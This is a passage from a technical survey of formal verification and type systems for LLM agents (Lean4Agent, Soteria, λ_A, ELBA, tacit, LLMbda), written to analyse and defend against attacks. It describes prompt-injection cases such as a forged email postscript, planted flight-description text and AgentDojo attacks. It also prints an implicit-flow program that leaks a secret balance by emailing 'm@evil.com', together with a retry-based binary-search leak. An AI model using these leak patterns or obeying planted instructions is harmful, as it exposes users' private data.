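To reason from one step to the next, Lean4Agent assumes that the model does what each contract promises. Wang and colleagues call this assumption *LLMExec* and include it in their library as an axiom, a statement that Lean accepts without proof. For every step and every environment env (the values of all the variables), it states

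pre(env) ⇒ there is an env′ such that post(env, env′).

This formula states that some environment satisfies the postcondition, but it doesn't mention the model or imply that the model will produce such an environment. It is also too strong as a general axiom. The library lets a developer define a step with any postcondition, including "false", which no environment satisfies. For that step, the axiom implies that such an environment exists, which is a contradiction, and Lean can prove any statement from a contradiction. The contract mismatches that Lean reports don't seem to depend on the axiom, but a proof that uses it would establish nothing by itself.

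The third layer checks after a run whether the model's output met the contract for each step. Lean and Python programs test the conditions that have a precise definition, and a language model judges the rest. In one run, the agent had to fix a bug in Django, a web framework. The contract for the "verify the fix" step required only that the evidence of verification be non-empty text. Lean confirmed that it was, although two tests were still failing. The test results then showed that the fix had not worked, and Lean4Agent traced the failure to this step.

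### Workflows that pass and workflows that succeed

Wang and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 write candidate workflows for two benchmarks. For each benchmark, they randomly chose three workflows that passed the second layer and three that failed it. Five models then ran them: GPT-5.2, GLM-5, Kimi-K2.5, Gemma-4-31B and Qwen-3.5-27B. The tasks were 50 hard software bugs from SWE-Bench-Verified and 100 multiple-choice questions about AI papers from ELAIP-Bench.

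| Benchmark | Passing workflows | Failing workflows | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| SWE-Bench-Verified | 58.27% | 43.47% | 14.80 points |
| ELAIP-Bench | 36.60% | 27.53% | 9.07 points |

Wang and colleagues' main result, reported as 11.94%, is the average of the two differences in percentage points. We can't use it to predict with certainty how any one workflow will perform. Even the workflows that passed left about 42% of the bugs unsolved.

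The difference also doesn't show that passing the check causes success. A carefully written workflow is more likely both to pass and to work, and the passing software workflows had better retry loops. Three workflows per group is a small sample, even with many tasks for each.

Many of the conditions are also advice about how to do the task well rather than tests of logical consistency. For example, one condition for multiple-choice questions requires the workflow to judge each option independently. Of the 40 candidate workflows for ELAIP-Bench, 21 failed with such conditions on the workflow as a whole, and only 8 failed without them. Part of the gain may therefore reflect the researchers' knowledge of what makes a good workflow.

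Repairing faulty workflows gives better evidence of cause and effect. In one software workflow that failed the check, each step started without the earlier conversation. When Wang and colleagues gave the steps access to it, the workflow passed, and the success rate rose from 52% to 62% for GPT-5.2 and from 48% to 60% for GLM-5. Repairing an ELAIP-Bench workflow raised GLM-5's score from 22% to 43%. Fixing defects that the checker had identified thus produced substantial gains, but in only two workflows.

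LeanEvolve revises a workflow after a failed run. The third layer identifies the step that probably went wrong, and a language model rewrites that step's instructions. On the software bugs, the revised workflows solved an additional 7.47% of the problems on average across the five models, ranging from 4.67% for GLM-5 to 10.67% for Qwen. Excluding revisions that a language model made without guidance from the checker, the gain was 5.07%.

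This comparison is between one attempt and two attempts at the same problems, with feedback before the second. In the Django example, the feedback included advice to run the tests that decide whether the benchmark counts the bug as fixed. A programmer working on a new bug may have no such tests. Wang and colleagues made a fairer comparison on ELAIP-Bench, using 20 problems that the agents had initially failed. Revisions guided by the checker solved about seven percentage points more of these problems than unguided revisions did, or between one and two extra solutions per model.

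### Where the proofs rely on the model

Unlike Moon and Varshney's proof for PocketFlow, Lean4Agent assumes that the model's answer meets a stated condition at every step the model performs. If the model follows an instruction injected into a bug report, LLMExec is false for that step, and the proof no longer applies to the run. The third layer may detect this, but only after the agent has acted.

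Soteria's proof relies less on the model. It covers only runs that follow the plan, but strict mode blocks departures from the plan, and in default mode the monitor checks every call. The proof also assumes that tools satisfy their postconditions. Soteria tests this after each call and stops if a postcondition fails, but by then the call has taken effect.

The proof depends directly on the model's judgement when a plan calls `llm_eval`. In an example from He and colleagues, a plan uses a model to select flights, and the step's postcondition requires at least one flight and enough seats on each. Dafny assumes this condition when it verifies the plan. During the run, Soteria checks the model's answer against the condition, queries the model again if the check fails, and halts after too many failures. The plan therefore never continues with a flight that lacks seats. But the condition doesn't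 restrict price, so text planted in a flight description could cause the model to pick the most expensive flight, which the plan would then book.

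## Types for programs that call language models (λ_A and language-based agent control)

Soteria depends on a solver, which may fail to find a proof even for a correct plan. A *type system* checks simpler conditions, which a compiler can usually decide by itself for any program. A *type* describes a kind of value, such as text or a pair of texts. A function's type states what the function takes and returns.

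Suppose a developer wants an agent to find Alice in the directory and then notify her. The directory returns a record, which is a pair made up of a name and an email address, while the notification step takes only an address:

```
lookup : Text → Text × Text
notify : Text → Text
```

The developer connects the two steps but forgets to take the address out of the record. In Python, which doesn't check types before running a program, the agent would contact the directory and then either crash or send the mail server a pair as if it were an address. A type checker rejects the program before it starts, because `Text × Text` is not `Text`. The developer can fix the program by adding a step in between that picks out the address.

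Such a check guarantees *type safety*, which usually has two parts. *Progress* means that a well-typed program that hasn't finished can always take another step. *Preservation* means that the program keeps the same type after each step. Together they imply that the program never gets stuck on a value of the wrong type. The program can still use an incorrect value, such as Bob's address instead of Alice's, because both addresses have the same type.

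### Model calls as functions on text

Liu (2026), in *λ_A*, applies this idea to agents. The lambda calculus is a minimal programming language in which everything is a function, and λ_A extends it with what agents need:

| Construct | Meaning |
|---|---|
| lam p θ | query a model with system prompt p and settings θ |
| tool[f] | call the outside function f |
| e₁ » e₂ | run e₁ and pass its result to e₂ |
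| fixₙ e | repeat e for a limited number of rounds |
| case | choose a branch according to a label |
| guard e P | run e, then test whether the result satisfies P |
| mem e σ | run e with a persistent memory σ |

The typing rule for connecting two steps is

```
Γ ⊢ e₁ : τ₁ → τ₂      Γ ⊢ e₂ : τ₂ → τ₃
───────────────────────────────────────
         Γ ⊢ e₁ » e₂ : τ₁ → τ₃
```

Γ lists the types of the variables in scope, and each τ stands for any type. If both statements above the line hold, so does the one below. Because τ₂ appears in both statements above the line, e₂ must accept the type that e₁ returns. For lookup » notify, τ₂ would have to be both `Text × Text` and `Text`, so the rule doesn't apply and the program has no type.

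Every model call in λ_A takes text and returns text, so the output of any call can be the input to any other. If a model is supposed to return an email address and answers "I couldn't find Alice", the answer still has the correct type. A guard can catch this at run time by testing whether the answer looks like an address. The type safety theorem therefore guarantees that a well-typed program either produces a value of its type or stops at a failed guard, which is a well-defined error.

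Liu notes that tools in real agent configurations mostly take and return text as well, so the types rule out little in practice. In the report task, the raw report and the sanitized one are both text, so λ_A would let the agent send either.

### When a bounded loop ends

An agent's main loop becomes a fix term. In simplified notation, with e as the body of the loop and v as the current state, it follows two rules:

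```
fix₀ e v  →  v
fixₙ e v  →  e (fixₙ₋₁ e) v       for n > 0
```

In each round, the body receives a copy of the loop with the counter reduced by one. The body can call this copy to continue or return a result to stop. When the counter reaches zero, the loop returns the current state, even if the agent has not finished its task.

Liu proves that the loop ends after at most n rounds if every model call and tool call returns. The theorem doesn't limit how long a round takes. If a mail server never answers, the agent waits forever mid-round, and the theorem no longer applies. To prevent this, the software around the tool needs a time limit after which it returns an error message as the tool's result.

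The proof also assumes that the body calls the loop at most once per round, which the typing rule for loops doesn't require. A body that computes loop(loop(x)) has a correct type too. If U(n) is the number of rounds such a program needs, then

U(0) = 0 and U(n) = 1 + 2·U(n − 1), so U(n) = 2ⁿ − 1.

With n = 20, the program would still end, after 1,048,575 rounds. The bound of n is correct for the ordinary agent loop, which calls itself once per round.

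Liu derives a cost limit from the termination bound by multiplying n by the price of the most expensive call. An agent with 20 steps and a price of one cent per call would cost at most 20 cents. This assumes one paid call per round, but the usual loop queries the model and then runs a tool. Liu's tests allow for two calls per round, and in one test the agent made 15 calls against a limit of 40. The price per call also has to cover the longest prompt, because the conversation grows with each round.

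### What the Rocq proofs cover

The Rocq development has 1,519 lines and 42 completed proofs, with no placeholders for missing proofs. It includes proofs of type safety and the termination theorem. The proofs treat models and tools as functions that always return, and cover only models that always give the same answer to the same prompt.

No proof covers the 4,903 lines of Python that run λ_A agents, including the compiler that translates YAML agent configurations into λ_A terms. Liu's conclusion lists correct compilation among the benefits of the work, but the paper does not prove that the compiler is correct. Proving a theorem like CompCert's would require a formal semantics for the source language, and YAML agent configurations have none.

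Liu relies instead on 125 tests, all of which passed. In 60 of them, a model carried out elementary operations such as logical AND or adding one. These tests show that the Python code handles the constructs as intended, but they provide little evidence about whether the compiler translates a real configuration correctly.

### Defects in 835 agent configurations

Liu also built a *lint* tool, which looks for likely mistakes in a configuration without running it, and applied it to 835 configurations from GitHub. It reported at least one error in 786 of them, or 94.1%. Some configurations had several:

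| Missing or faulty item | Configurations | Share |
|---|---|---|
| tool for ending the loop | 483 | 57.8% |
| system prompt | 282 | 33.8% |
| choice of model | 51 | 6.1% |
| step limit | 1 | 0.1% |

Most of these are not bugs. Of the 483 configurations without a tool for ending the loop, 300 use a framework that ends it in its own code, 95 others set a maximum number of steps, and 88 have neither. More than half of all the configurations are for CrewAI, a framework whose users define their tools in Python, so the YAML file is incomplete by design.

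To test the tool, Liu planted 42 faults in ten working configurations. The tool found them all and raised no false alarms on the originals. He then checked 50 reported errors from frameworks other than CrewAI by reading the surrounding code. In 27 cases the item reported missing was absent everywhere, and in the other 23 the Python code or an environment variable supplied it. When the tool also searched the Python code, it recognized 22 of those 23 false alarms. The sample includes 14 errors about step limits, but the results for all 835 configurations list only one, and this discrepancy is unexplained.

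Liu didn't run the flagged agents to see whether they failed, so even an item that is really missing may do no harm. His soundness theorem for the lint rules states that every reported error is a defect under λ_A's semantics. In the proof, he claims that an empty system prompt makes the model's output as random as possible. None of λ_A's rules implies this, and real models answer questions well without a system prompt. Liu doesn't include the soundness theorem in his list of results checked in Rocq.

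### Types as policies

Types can do more than describe the shape of data. In Haskell, a function's type also records which effects the function may have. A program of type `Int` computes a whole number and does nothing else, while a program that reads files or contacts a server has a type marked `IO`. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use this to restrict what a model's code can do. Their Haskell library, ELBA, provides a function that a developer can call anywhere in a program:

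```
agent : Definitions → Prompt → t
```

The definitions are the types and functions the model may use, and t is the type of result the developer expects. The model writes a program, and the compiler checks that it has type t. If the check fails, ELBA sends the error message back to the model for another attempt. Otherwise, ELBA runs the program and returns its result.

For example, a public calculator might expect an `Int`. A user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute a factorial, and the model writes a program that does both. Deleting files is an `IO` operation, which makes the whole program `IO`, so the compiler rejects it before any files are deleted.

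Most agents need some effects, and for those the developer defines a custom effect type. In Zhou and colleagues' main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry it writes must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. In simplified form, the library contains three functions:

```
search : Text → BibIO (list of paper IDs)
fetch  : ID → BibIO (Trusted Entry)
append : Trusted Entry → BibIO ()
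```

The expected result type is `BibIO ()`, the type of programs that return no value and have only the effects the library allows. The general function for writing files has type `IO`, so the model can't use it here. It can't make up an entry either, because the library hides the constructor of `Trusted` and only `fetch` produces values of that type. The model's program can still sort and filter entries, and it can pick the wrong paper.

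The same method would work for part of the report task. If only Sanitize could produce text of type `Clean`, and Send accepted nothing else, a program that sends the raw report would fail to compile. A program that sends the clean text twice would still compile, because it has the same type as one that sends it once. Zhou and colleagues mention *linear types*, which limit how often a program can use a value, as a possible extension for one-time permissions.

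Some policies also need checks at run time. ELBA's file library represents each permitted location by a `Path` value, which a program can only narrow to something inside the same folder. When it does, the library resolves any `..` or symbolic link and refuses a result outside the folder. Simply comparing path prefixes, as PocketFlow's policy may do, would miss a path that leaves the folder this way.

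Unlike a Soteria or SPA plan, an ELBA program doesn't have to cover every case in advance. It can fetch one search result, put it in a new prompt and call `agent` again to decide what to do next. The compiler infers the type of this nested call from the surrounding code, so a subagent inside a `BibIO` program can use only `BibIO` effects. A program can give its subagents a stricter type, but not a looser one.

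### The transfer theorem

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a typed language preserves whatever its type system guarantees. Their formal version of the agent call carries a result type t and a bound n on the depth of nested subagents:

agentₜⁿ : Definitions → Prompt → Option t

A value of type `Option t` is either `Some result` or `Nothing`. An agent with bound n can write programs whose own agent calls have bounds of at most n − 1. The agent returns `Nothing` if n is zero or if the model's program doesn't pass the type checker. A practical system would usually retry a few times before giving up.

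Let L be the host language and traces(e) the set of all traces of a program e, where a trace records the tool calls with observable side effects. A *type system property* for t is a condition P on sets of traces that satisfies

e : t in L ⇒ P(traces(e)), for every program e.

For `BibIO ()`, P might be "every entry written to the file came from DBLP". Since P applies to a whole set of traces, it can also express properties that compare several runs, such as noninterference. The theorem is that every type system property of L is also a type system property of L extended with agent calls.

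The proof turns a program with agents into an ordinary program in L by substitution:

1. For bound 0, define an ordinary function a⁰ that always returns Nothing.
2. For bound n + 1, define a function aⁿ⁺¹ that obtains a program from the model and checks its type. If the check succeeds, it replaces every agent call in that program with the corresponding function for a smaller bound, then runs the result.
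3. Replace the agent calls in the developer's program in the same way. The new program is in L and has the same type as the original.
4. Show by induction on n that each replacement leaves the set of traces unchanged. P holds for the new program because it is an ordinary L program of type t, so P also holds for the original.

The bound matters in the definition of aⁿ⁺¹, which uses only functions with smaller bounds. Without it, the definition would be circular.

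The proof is on paper and is not machine-checked. It assumes that L can check and run program text during execution, and that the oracle is an arbitrary but fixed function from prompts to programs.

The theorem's usefulness depends on the guarantee it transfers. If the developer asks for a program of type `IO ()`, the model's code may do anything that `IO` allows. If the library exposes the constructor of `Trusted` by mistake, the model's code can forge entries. Standard Haskell also has `unsafePerformIO`, which hides effects inside a value whose type permits none. The guarantee therefore requires the model's code to stay within Safe Haskell, a restricted mode that excludes this function. The Haskell compiler and the policy libraries remain in the trusted base.

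Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with an ordinary agent on 100 bibliography tasks, using Claude Sonnet 5 for both. The ordinary agent got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, while ELBA made no such errors in 925. They also tested ELBA on the Slack tasks from AgentDojo, with policies from an existing Haskell library that tracks labels at runtime. Normal attacks failed on every model even without policies, so Zhou and colleagues modified ELBA to make its subagents obey any planted instruction. Without policies, between 425 and 621 of 735 attacks then failed, depending on the model. With policies, every attack failed, though the benchmark wrongly scored a few runs as successful attacks. The policies also blocked legitimate actions, so Claude Opus 4.7 completed 351 tasks instead of 523.

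### Secrets that the model must not see

The transfer theorem's traces omit an important effect, the query to the model itself. A calculator of type `Int` supposedly has no effects, but it sends its prompt to the company that runs the model. If the prompt contains a secret, the calculator discloses it to that company without violating the type.

The system tacit, which Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) describe in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, is designed for this problem. It treats the cloud model as an adversary and makes it act through programs in Scala. A *capability* is a value that permits an effect. For example, a program can write to a file only if it holds a handle f for that file. An experimental Scala feature called capture checking records in a function's type which capabilities the function holds:

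```
String -> String         holds no capabilities
String ->{f} String      may use the file handle f
```

When a program reads a secret file, tacit returns the text inside a container called `Classified`. The container's `map` operation applies a function to the secret and puts the result in a new container. It accepts only functions without capabilities:

```
secret.map(s => s.toUpperCase)           accepted
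secret.map(s => { f.write(s); s })       rejected
```

The cloud model can thus write a program that processes the secret without receiving the secret itself. If the program prints the container, the model gets only asterisks, while the user's terminal shows the text. To summarize a secret contract, the program can pass the container to a separate, trusted model, which also returns its answer in a container.

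Capture checking also limits how long a permission lasts. A program gets access to a folder only within a block of code. If the block returns a function that would read a file later, the compiler rejects the code because the function's type mentions a capability that doesn't exist outside the block.

The type system underlying capture checking has machine-checked proofs. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) adds a Lean 4 proof of type safety for an extension that groups capabilities by kind. But tacit also relies on Scala's *safe mode*, which bans features such as reflection and unchecked type casts that could hide a capability. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet proved that safe mode provides its intended guarantees. The trusted base includes the Scala compiler, tacit's library of about 1,000 lines and the trusted model.

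Odersky and colleagues tested tacit on a software project with a folder of secrets. Each model went through 120 trials that combined a user task with a prompt injection and 11 in which the user asked for the secrets directly or under a pretext. This table shows in how many trials a secret appeared in the agent's output:

| Model | Injections, plain text | Direct requests, plain text | All trials, `Classified` |
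|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0 of 120 | 2 of 11 | 0 of 131 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 3 of 120 | 8 of 11 | 0 of 131 |

With the secrets in containers, the agents still completed 99.2% of tasks with Sonnet and 90.0% with MiniMax. The trials measured only leaks through the agent's output. A function without capabilities can still run longer for some secrets than for others, and Odersky and colleagues say that tacit doesn't prevent leaks through timing. The type system also doesn't cover external commands, so the administrator has to restrict which ones the agent may run.

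### The cost of writing typed programs

Odersky and colleagues found that models did almost no worse at their tasks when they had to write typed Scala instead of requesting tool calls. On the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, success rates were 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with tacit than with ordinary tool calls for all three models tested. On 300 software bugs from SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax solved 41.7% with tacit and 43.3% without. The compiler rejected at most 8% of the programs on τ²-bench, and the models usually fixed the error at the first or second retry. ELBA's models, which write Haskell, also needed few retries, about one per eight runs on average. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it queries the model again when new data arrives.

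*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same group as tacit, did worse. It adds a typed agent call like ELBA's to Scala. Its types don't limit how deeply agent calls can nest, so a developer who wants a limit has to set one at runtime. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls, a gap described in the paper's abstract as "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, solved 29.1% and 33.2%, respectively.

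LACUNA's compiler checks each program as a whole, and none of the program runs if the check fails. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, an agent has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as a number, but the model's program subtracts correctly and then returns a sentence. An interpreter without type checking would subtract the 50 before it reached the error, and a retry could subtract another 50. LACUNA rejects the program, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again. A model that writes poor Scala therefore does no damage this way, but it may not complete its task. On τ²-bench's telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the programs that Flash-Lite wrote.

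## A proof about where secret and untrusted data can flow (LLMbda)

The labels in Agenra are accurate only if the developer correctly declares the dependencies between values. LLMbda tracks these dependencies automatically by attaching a label to every value and updating the labels at every step of a program, a technique called *information-flow control*. Garby and colleagues prove that secret inputs can't influence a public result and that untrusted inputs can't influence a trusted one, except by making a program stop early or run forever.

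### One model to plan and another to read

Garby and colleagues adapt an example from CaMeL in which a user asks her agent to send Bob a reminder about a meeting he mentioned in an email. An attacker, writing in Bob's name, has added a postscript to the email that asks for a cancellation note instead. When the request and the email were in the same conversation, GPT-4o sent the cancellation.

In 2023, the programmer Simon Willison proposed the *dual-LLM pattern* to prevent this. A privileged model plans the work and requests tool calls but never reads untrusted data. A quarantined model reads that data but can only return values. For the reminder, the privileged model writes a program that fetches the email, has the quarantined model extract the sender's address, and sends a fixed text to that address. As in Meijer's design, the plan is complete before the agent fetches the email, so the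 email can't change it and the agent still sends a reminder.

However, the postscript can still cause the quarantined model to return the attacker's address, and the agent then sends the reminder there. Keeping the models apart protects the choice of actions but not the data that the actions use, so CaMeL and FIDES, two defences from 2025, combine the pattern with labels.

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes its plan in a restricted subset of Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) describes how the interpreter labels inputs by their source and enforces policies as the plan runs. It argues that Python is a poor basis for strong information-flow guarantees because features such as exceptions and reflection make programs hard to analyse, and it recommends a small language designed for security instead.

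FIDES uses a fixed agent loop. In a simple loop with labels, one untrusted tool result makes the whole conversation untrusted, and the agent can no longer use any tool that requires trusted input. According to *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), FIDES therefore stores a result in a variable if adding it to the conversation would raise the conversation's label. The planner receives all other results in full. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that the agent can't base an action on a variable's content without further secure processing. One way to inspect a variable is constrained decoding, which restricts a model's answer to a fixed format such as "yes" or "no".

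FIDES has a noninterference theorem, but the theorem covers only FIDES's own loop and assumes a model that always gives the same answer to the same input. Its guarantee for secrets is weaker still, because it doesn't cover secrets that leak through a program's choice of branch. CaMeL is more flexible, since its privileged model can write many different programs, but it has no noninterference theorem. The CaMeL paper calls a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for future work.

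### A leak through a branch that is not taken

Suppose an agent manages a bank account, and an attacker wants to know whether the balance is above some threshold. The direct attempt is

```
if balance > threshold:  send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL blocks the email. The condition depends on a secret, so CaMeL treats everything inside the branch as depending on that secret too.

Garby and colleagues describe an indirect version that gets through. A program that works this way is:

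```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Both variables start out public. Let the threshold be $500. Here is what happens for a balance of $900 and for one of $100:

| Line | Balance $900 | Balance $100 |
|---|---|---|
| if balance > threshold | taken: tmp becomes False and secret | not taken: tmp stays True and public |
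| if tmp | not taken: rich stays True and public | taken: rich becomes False and public |
| if rich | taken: the email goes out | not taken: no email |

The attacker gets an email exactly when the balance is above $500. In both runs, `rich` is public when the program reaches the last line, so CaMeL does not block the email.

With the $900 balance, `rich` depends on the secret because the program would have changed it if the balance had been lower. But the assignment to `rich` didn't run, so its label didn't change. With the $100 balance, that assignment did run, but `tmp` was still public because the assignment to `tmp` hadn't run. A monitor that updates labels only when code runs can't detect a dependence on code that didn't run. Fenton first described this kind of leak in the 1970s.

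In 2009, Austin and Flanagan proposed a remedy called *no-high-upgrade*, which stops any program that tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. With the $900 balance, the program would stop at `tmp = False`. No email would go out in either case, but anyone who could tell that the program had stopped would still learn the balance was high.

One such yes-or-no answer may be harmless, but CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries failed plans, and no labels cover that loop. The loop can therefore run a program with one threshold and set the next according to whether a policy blocked it. It can find a balance between $0 and $1,023 in ten runs by halving the range each time. CaMeL censors its error messages, which reduces this leak but is not guaranteed to stop it. Garby and colleagues also found that inserting an untrusted value into text in CaMeL made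 the value trusted.

### Conversations and labels in LLMbda

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, as λ_A does, but has no static types. It treats the conversation with the model as something a program can control:

| Construct | Meaning |
|---|---|
| send e | add the value of e to the conversation as a prompt |
| recv | get the model's response, parse it as code and run that code |
| fork e | run e on a copy of the conversation, then return to the original |
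| clear | empty the conversation |

The shorthand `@e` means `send e`, then `recv`. A response can be as simple as the number 5, which is a program that returns 5. It can also be a function, which the agent can then call.

A developer can build the quarantined model out of these constructs. The program forks the conversation, clears the copy, sends it the untrusted text, and keeps only the value that comes back, so the text never enters the main conversation. This separation is part of the architecture in CaMeL and FIDES. In LLMbda it is a few lines of code, and the theorem still applies if a developer changes them.

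A label is a set that may contain U for untrusted and S for secret. There are four possibilities: ∅, {U}, {S} and {U, S}. Data labelled l may flow to a place labelled m, written l ⊑ m, if l is a subset of m. Combining two values joins their labels, which here means taking the union. For example, comparing a secret balance with a public threshold gives

{S} : 900 > ∅ : 500 = {S} : true.

Every step also has its own label, pc (for "program counter"), which records what influenced the decision to take that step. The pc starts as ∅. LLMbda treats `if` as a call to a function that selects one of the two branches. That function carries the condition's label, and its body runs with this label as pc. Everything inside `if {S}:true` therefore runs with pc = {S}, and every value it produces carries at least that label.

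The conversation has a single label, the join of the labels of all messages sent so far, and each response gets this label too. This rule is cautious, since the model may have ignored the one untrusted sentence in a long prompt, but nobody can tell from outside whether it did. DAPLab's *GIF* (2026), a project description from a Columbia University research group, points out that any input token can influence any output token, so labels this coarse spread quickly. Forking and clearing limit the spread by keeping untrusted text in a separate conversation.

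Data without a label counts as public and trusted. If a developer forgets to label the emails in an inbox as untrusted, the theorem still holds, but it doesn't protect the agent from them.

### The rule for sending a prompt

Variables in LLMbda never change their value, so nobody can write the program with `tmp` and `rich` in it directly. But the conversation does change, and the same leak could happen there. The rule for `send` prevents it:

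```
pc ⊢ C, e ⇓ l:c, V ▷ w, s      flatten(V) = n:v      pc ⊑ l
──────────────────────────────────────────────────────────────
pc ⊢ C, send e ⇓ (l ⊔ n) : (c + serialise(v)), pc:() ▷ w, s
```

As in λ_A's typing rule, the statement below the line holds if all the statements above it do. The first means that, starting from conversation C, the expression e produces the value V and leaves a conversation c with label l, while the model gives the responses listed in s with combined probability w. The second collects the labels inside V, however deeply nested, into a single label n, leaving the plain value v. The third is the security check, which requires the current step's label to be within the conversation's label.

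The line below states the result. The program converts v to text and adds it to the conversation, whose label becomes the join of l and n. The send returns only an empty value.

Here is an attempt to leak a secret through the conversation, in simplified notation:

```
@"Remember this value: x = false"
if secret then @"Set x = true" else ()
@"Give me the value of x"
```

The first prompt is public, so the conversation keeps the label ∅. If the secret is true, the program enters the branch with pc = {S} and tries to send. The check requires {S} ⊑ ∅, which does not hold, so the program stops. If the secret is false, the program skips the branch, and the model presumably answers "false", which is public.

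Raising the conversation's label to {S} and letting the program continue would still leak the secret. The final answer would be labeled secret when the secret is true and public when it is false, so someone who could read only public values would see an answer only when the secret is false. The leak would come from the label itself depending on the secret, as in the CaMeL example.

A developer can repair the program by labelling the first prompt {S}, even though its text is not secret. The conversation is then labelled secret from the start, whichever branch the program takes. Both runs finish with the final answer labelled secret.

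The rules for receiving a response and clearing the conversation include the same check, because both operations also change the conversation. Together these checks give a result that Garby and colleagues call *confinement*. If a step runs with label pc, either it leaves the conversation unchanged, or the conversation's label includes pc both before and after the step. Code in a secret branch therefore cannot change a public conversation.

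### What an observer can tell apart

Noninterference compares two runs whose inputs differ only in ways that an observer can't see. An observer at level n sees the values whose labels are within n. For secrecy, the observer is at {U} and sees all public data, trusted or not. For protection against prompt injection, the observer is at {S} and sees all trusted data.

Two expressions are *indistinguishable* at level n, written e₀ ~ₙ e₁, if they are the same except for parts whose labels an observer at level n can't see. For example, an observer at {U} can't distinguish a program containing {S}:900 from the same program with {S}:100 instead. Two conversations are indistinguishable if they are identical or the observer can see neither.

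A program can also test a value's label, and the result could leak information if it isn't labelled correctly. Suppose a program tests whether a value's label is within {U}, and the value is labelled {U} in one run and {S} in another. An observer at ∅ can't see the value in either run, but the test succeeds in the first and fails in the second. If the result were labelled ∅, the observer could tell the runs apart.

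LLMbda therefore labels the result of a test with the limit it was tested against, here {U}, which hides the result from this observer. The same reasoning works for any limit l. An observer at n can see the result only if l ⊑ n. If this observer can't see a value, the value's label is not ⊑ n, so it is not ⊑ l either, and the test fails in both runs. An earlier design by Austin and Flanagan left the limit's label off the result, which is safe only if there are just two labels.

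### Programs as probability distributions

Because an LLM's answers vary, Garby and colleagues' version of noninterference compares probabilities. If the model always gave the same answers, noninterference would only require indistinguishable inputs to produce indistinguishable results.

They illustrate the idea with a program that asks the model to flip a biased coin twice and returns the number of heads. Suppose the model answers heads with a probability of exactly 0.3. The probability of a run is the product of the probabilities of its responses, so two heads have probability 0.3 × 0.3 = 0.09. If each flip takes place in a fork, nothing remains in the conversation, and the two ways of getting one head end in the same state. Their probabilities add up:

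| Heads | Probability |
|---|---|
| 0 | 0.7 × 0.7 = 0.49 |
| 1 | 0.3 × 0.7 + 0.7 × 0.3 = 0.42 |
| 2 | 0.3 × 0.3 = 0.09 |

These probabilities add up to 1 because this program always finishes. A program that runs forever or is stopped by a label check never reaches a final state, so the probabilities of the final states add up to less than 1. The missing part is the probability of *nontermination*, and the result is called a *subdistribution*. Adding the probabilities of all final states that look the same at level m gives what an observer at that level sees.

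The strictest form of noninterference would require the two subdistributions to be equal, including their missing parts. LLMbda can't satisfy that, because its label checks sometimes stop a program for one value of a secret and not for the other. Consider this program:

```
coin = @"Flip a fair coin"
if coin = "tails" then
  if secret then @"Carry on" else ()
return coin
```

If the secret is false, the program returns heads or tails with probability 0.5 each. If the secret is true, it returns heads with probability 0.5 and never returns tails, because when the coin lands tails, the program tries to send a prompt from a secret branch and the check stops it.

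Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish, but found that this was the wrong definition. In the coin program, heads has probability 0.5 among finished runs if the secret is false and 1 if it is true. The comparison would therefore reject the program, although the secret only stopped some of the runs.

### Compatible distributions

The definition they settled on comes from a general method published by Hunt, Sands and Stucki in 2023. Two subdistributions μ and ν are *compatible*, written μ ⌣ ν, if there is a third subdistribution ω with

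μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q.

The two could become equal if the runs that never finish did finish in suitable ways. For the coin program, ω gives heads and tails a probability of 0.5 each.

The smallest candidate for ω takes the larger of the two probabilities for each outcome, so μ and ν are compatible exactly when these larger values add up to at most 1. Suppose a program answers "yes" or "no", and consider three possible subdistributions:

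| | Yes | No | Missing |
|---|---|---|---|
| μ | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| ν | 0.4 | 0.4 | 0.2 |
| ρ | 0.2 | 0.6 | 0.2 |

For μ and ν, the larger values are 0.5 and 0.4, which add up to 0.9, so μ and ν are compatible. For μ and ρ, the larger values are 0.5 and 0.6, which add up to 1.1, so μ and ρ are incompatible. Nontermination alone can't explain the difference between μ and ρ, because even if all of μ's missing runs had ended in "no", its probability of "no" would be only 0.5, which is less than ρ's 0.6.

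Compatibility also limits how much a secret can change the visible results. Let Δ be half the sum of the differences between the two probabilities of each outcome, and let div be the missing probability. Garby and colleagues prove that compatible subdistributions satisfy

Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2.

For μ and ν, Δ is (0.1 + 0.1) / 2 = 0.1, and the limit is (0.2 + 0.2) / 2 = 0.2. For μ and ρ, Δ is 0.3, which exceeds the limit. The bound follows from the fact that the difference between two numbers is twice the larger one minus their sum:

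Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| = 2 Σ max(μ(q), ν(q)) − Σ μ(q) − Σ ν(q)
≤ 2 − Σ μ(q) − Σ ν(q) = div(μ) + div(ν).

The inequality holds because the larger values add up to at most 1. Dividing both sides by two gives the bound.

If both runs are certain to finish, the bound is zero and the two distributions must be equal. If the program often stops early, the bound lets them differ a lot. For example, the program that tries to leak a secret through the value x always stops early when the secret is true. When the secret is false, it always returns "false", provided the model answers reliably. Δ and the bound are then both 0.5, and an observer who notices whether the program stopped early learns the secret.

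### The theorem

Garby and colleagues call their property *termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference*, or TIPNI. In the following formula, ⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧ₘ stands for the subdistribution that an observer at level m sees when the program e starts with conversation C:

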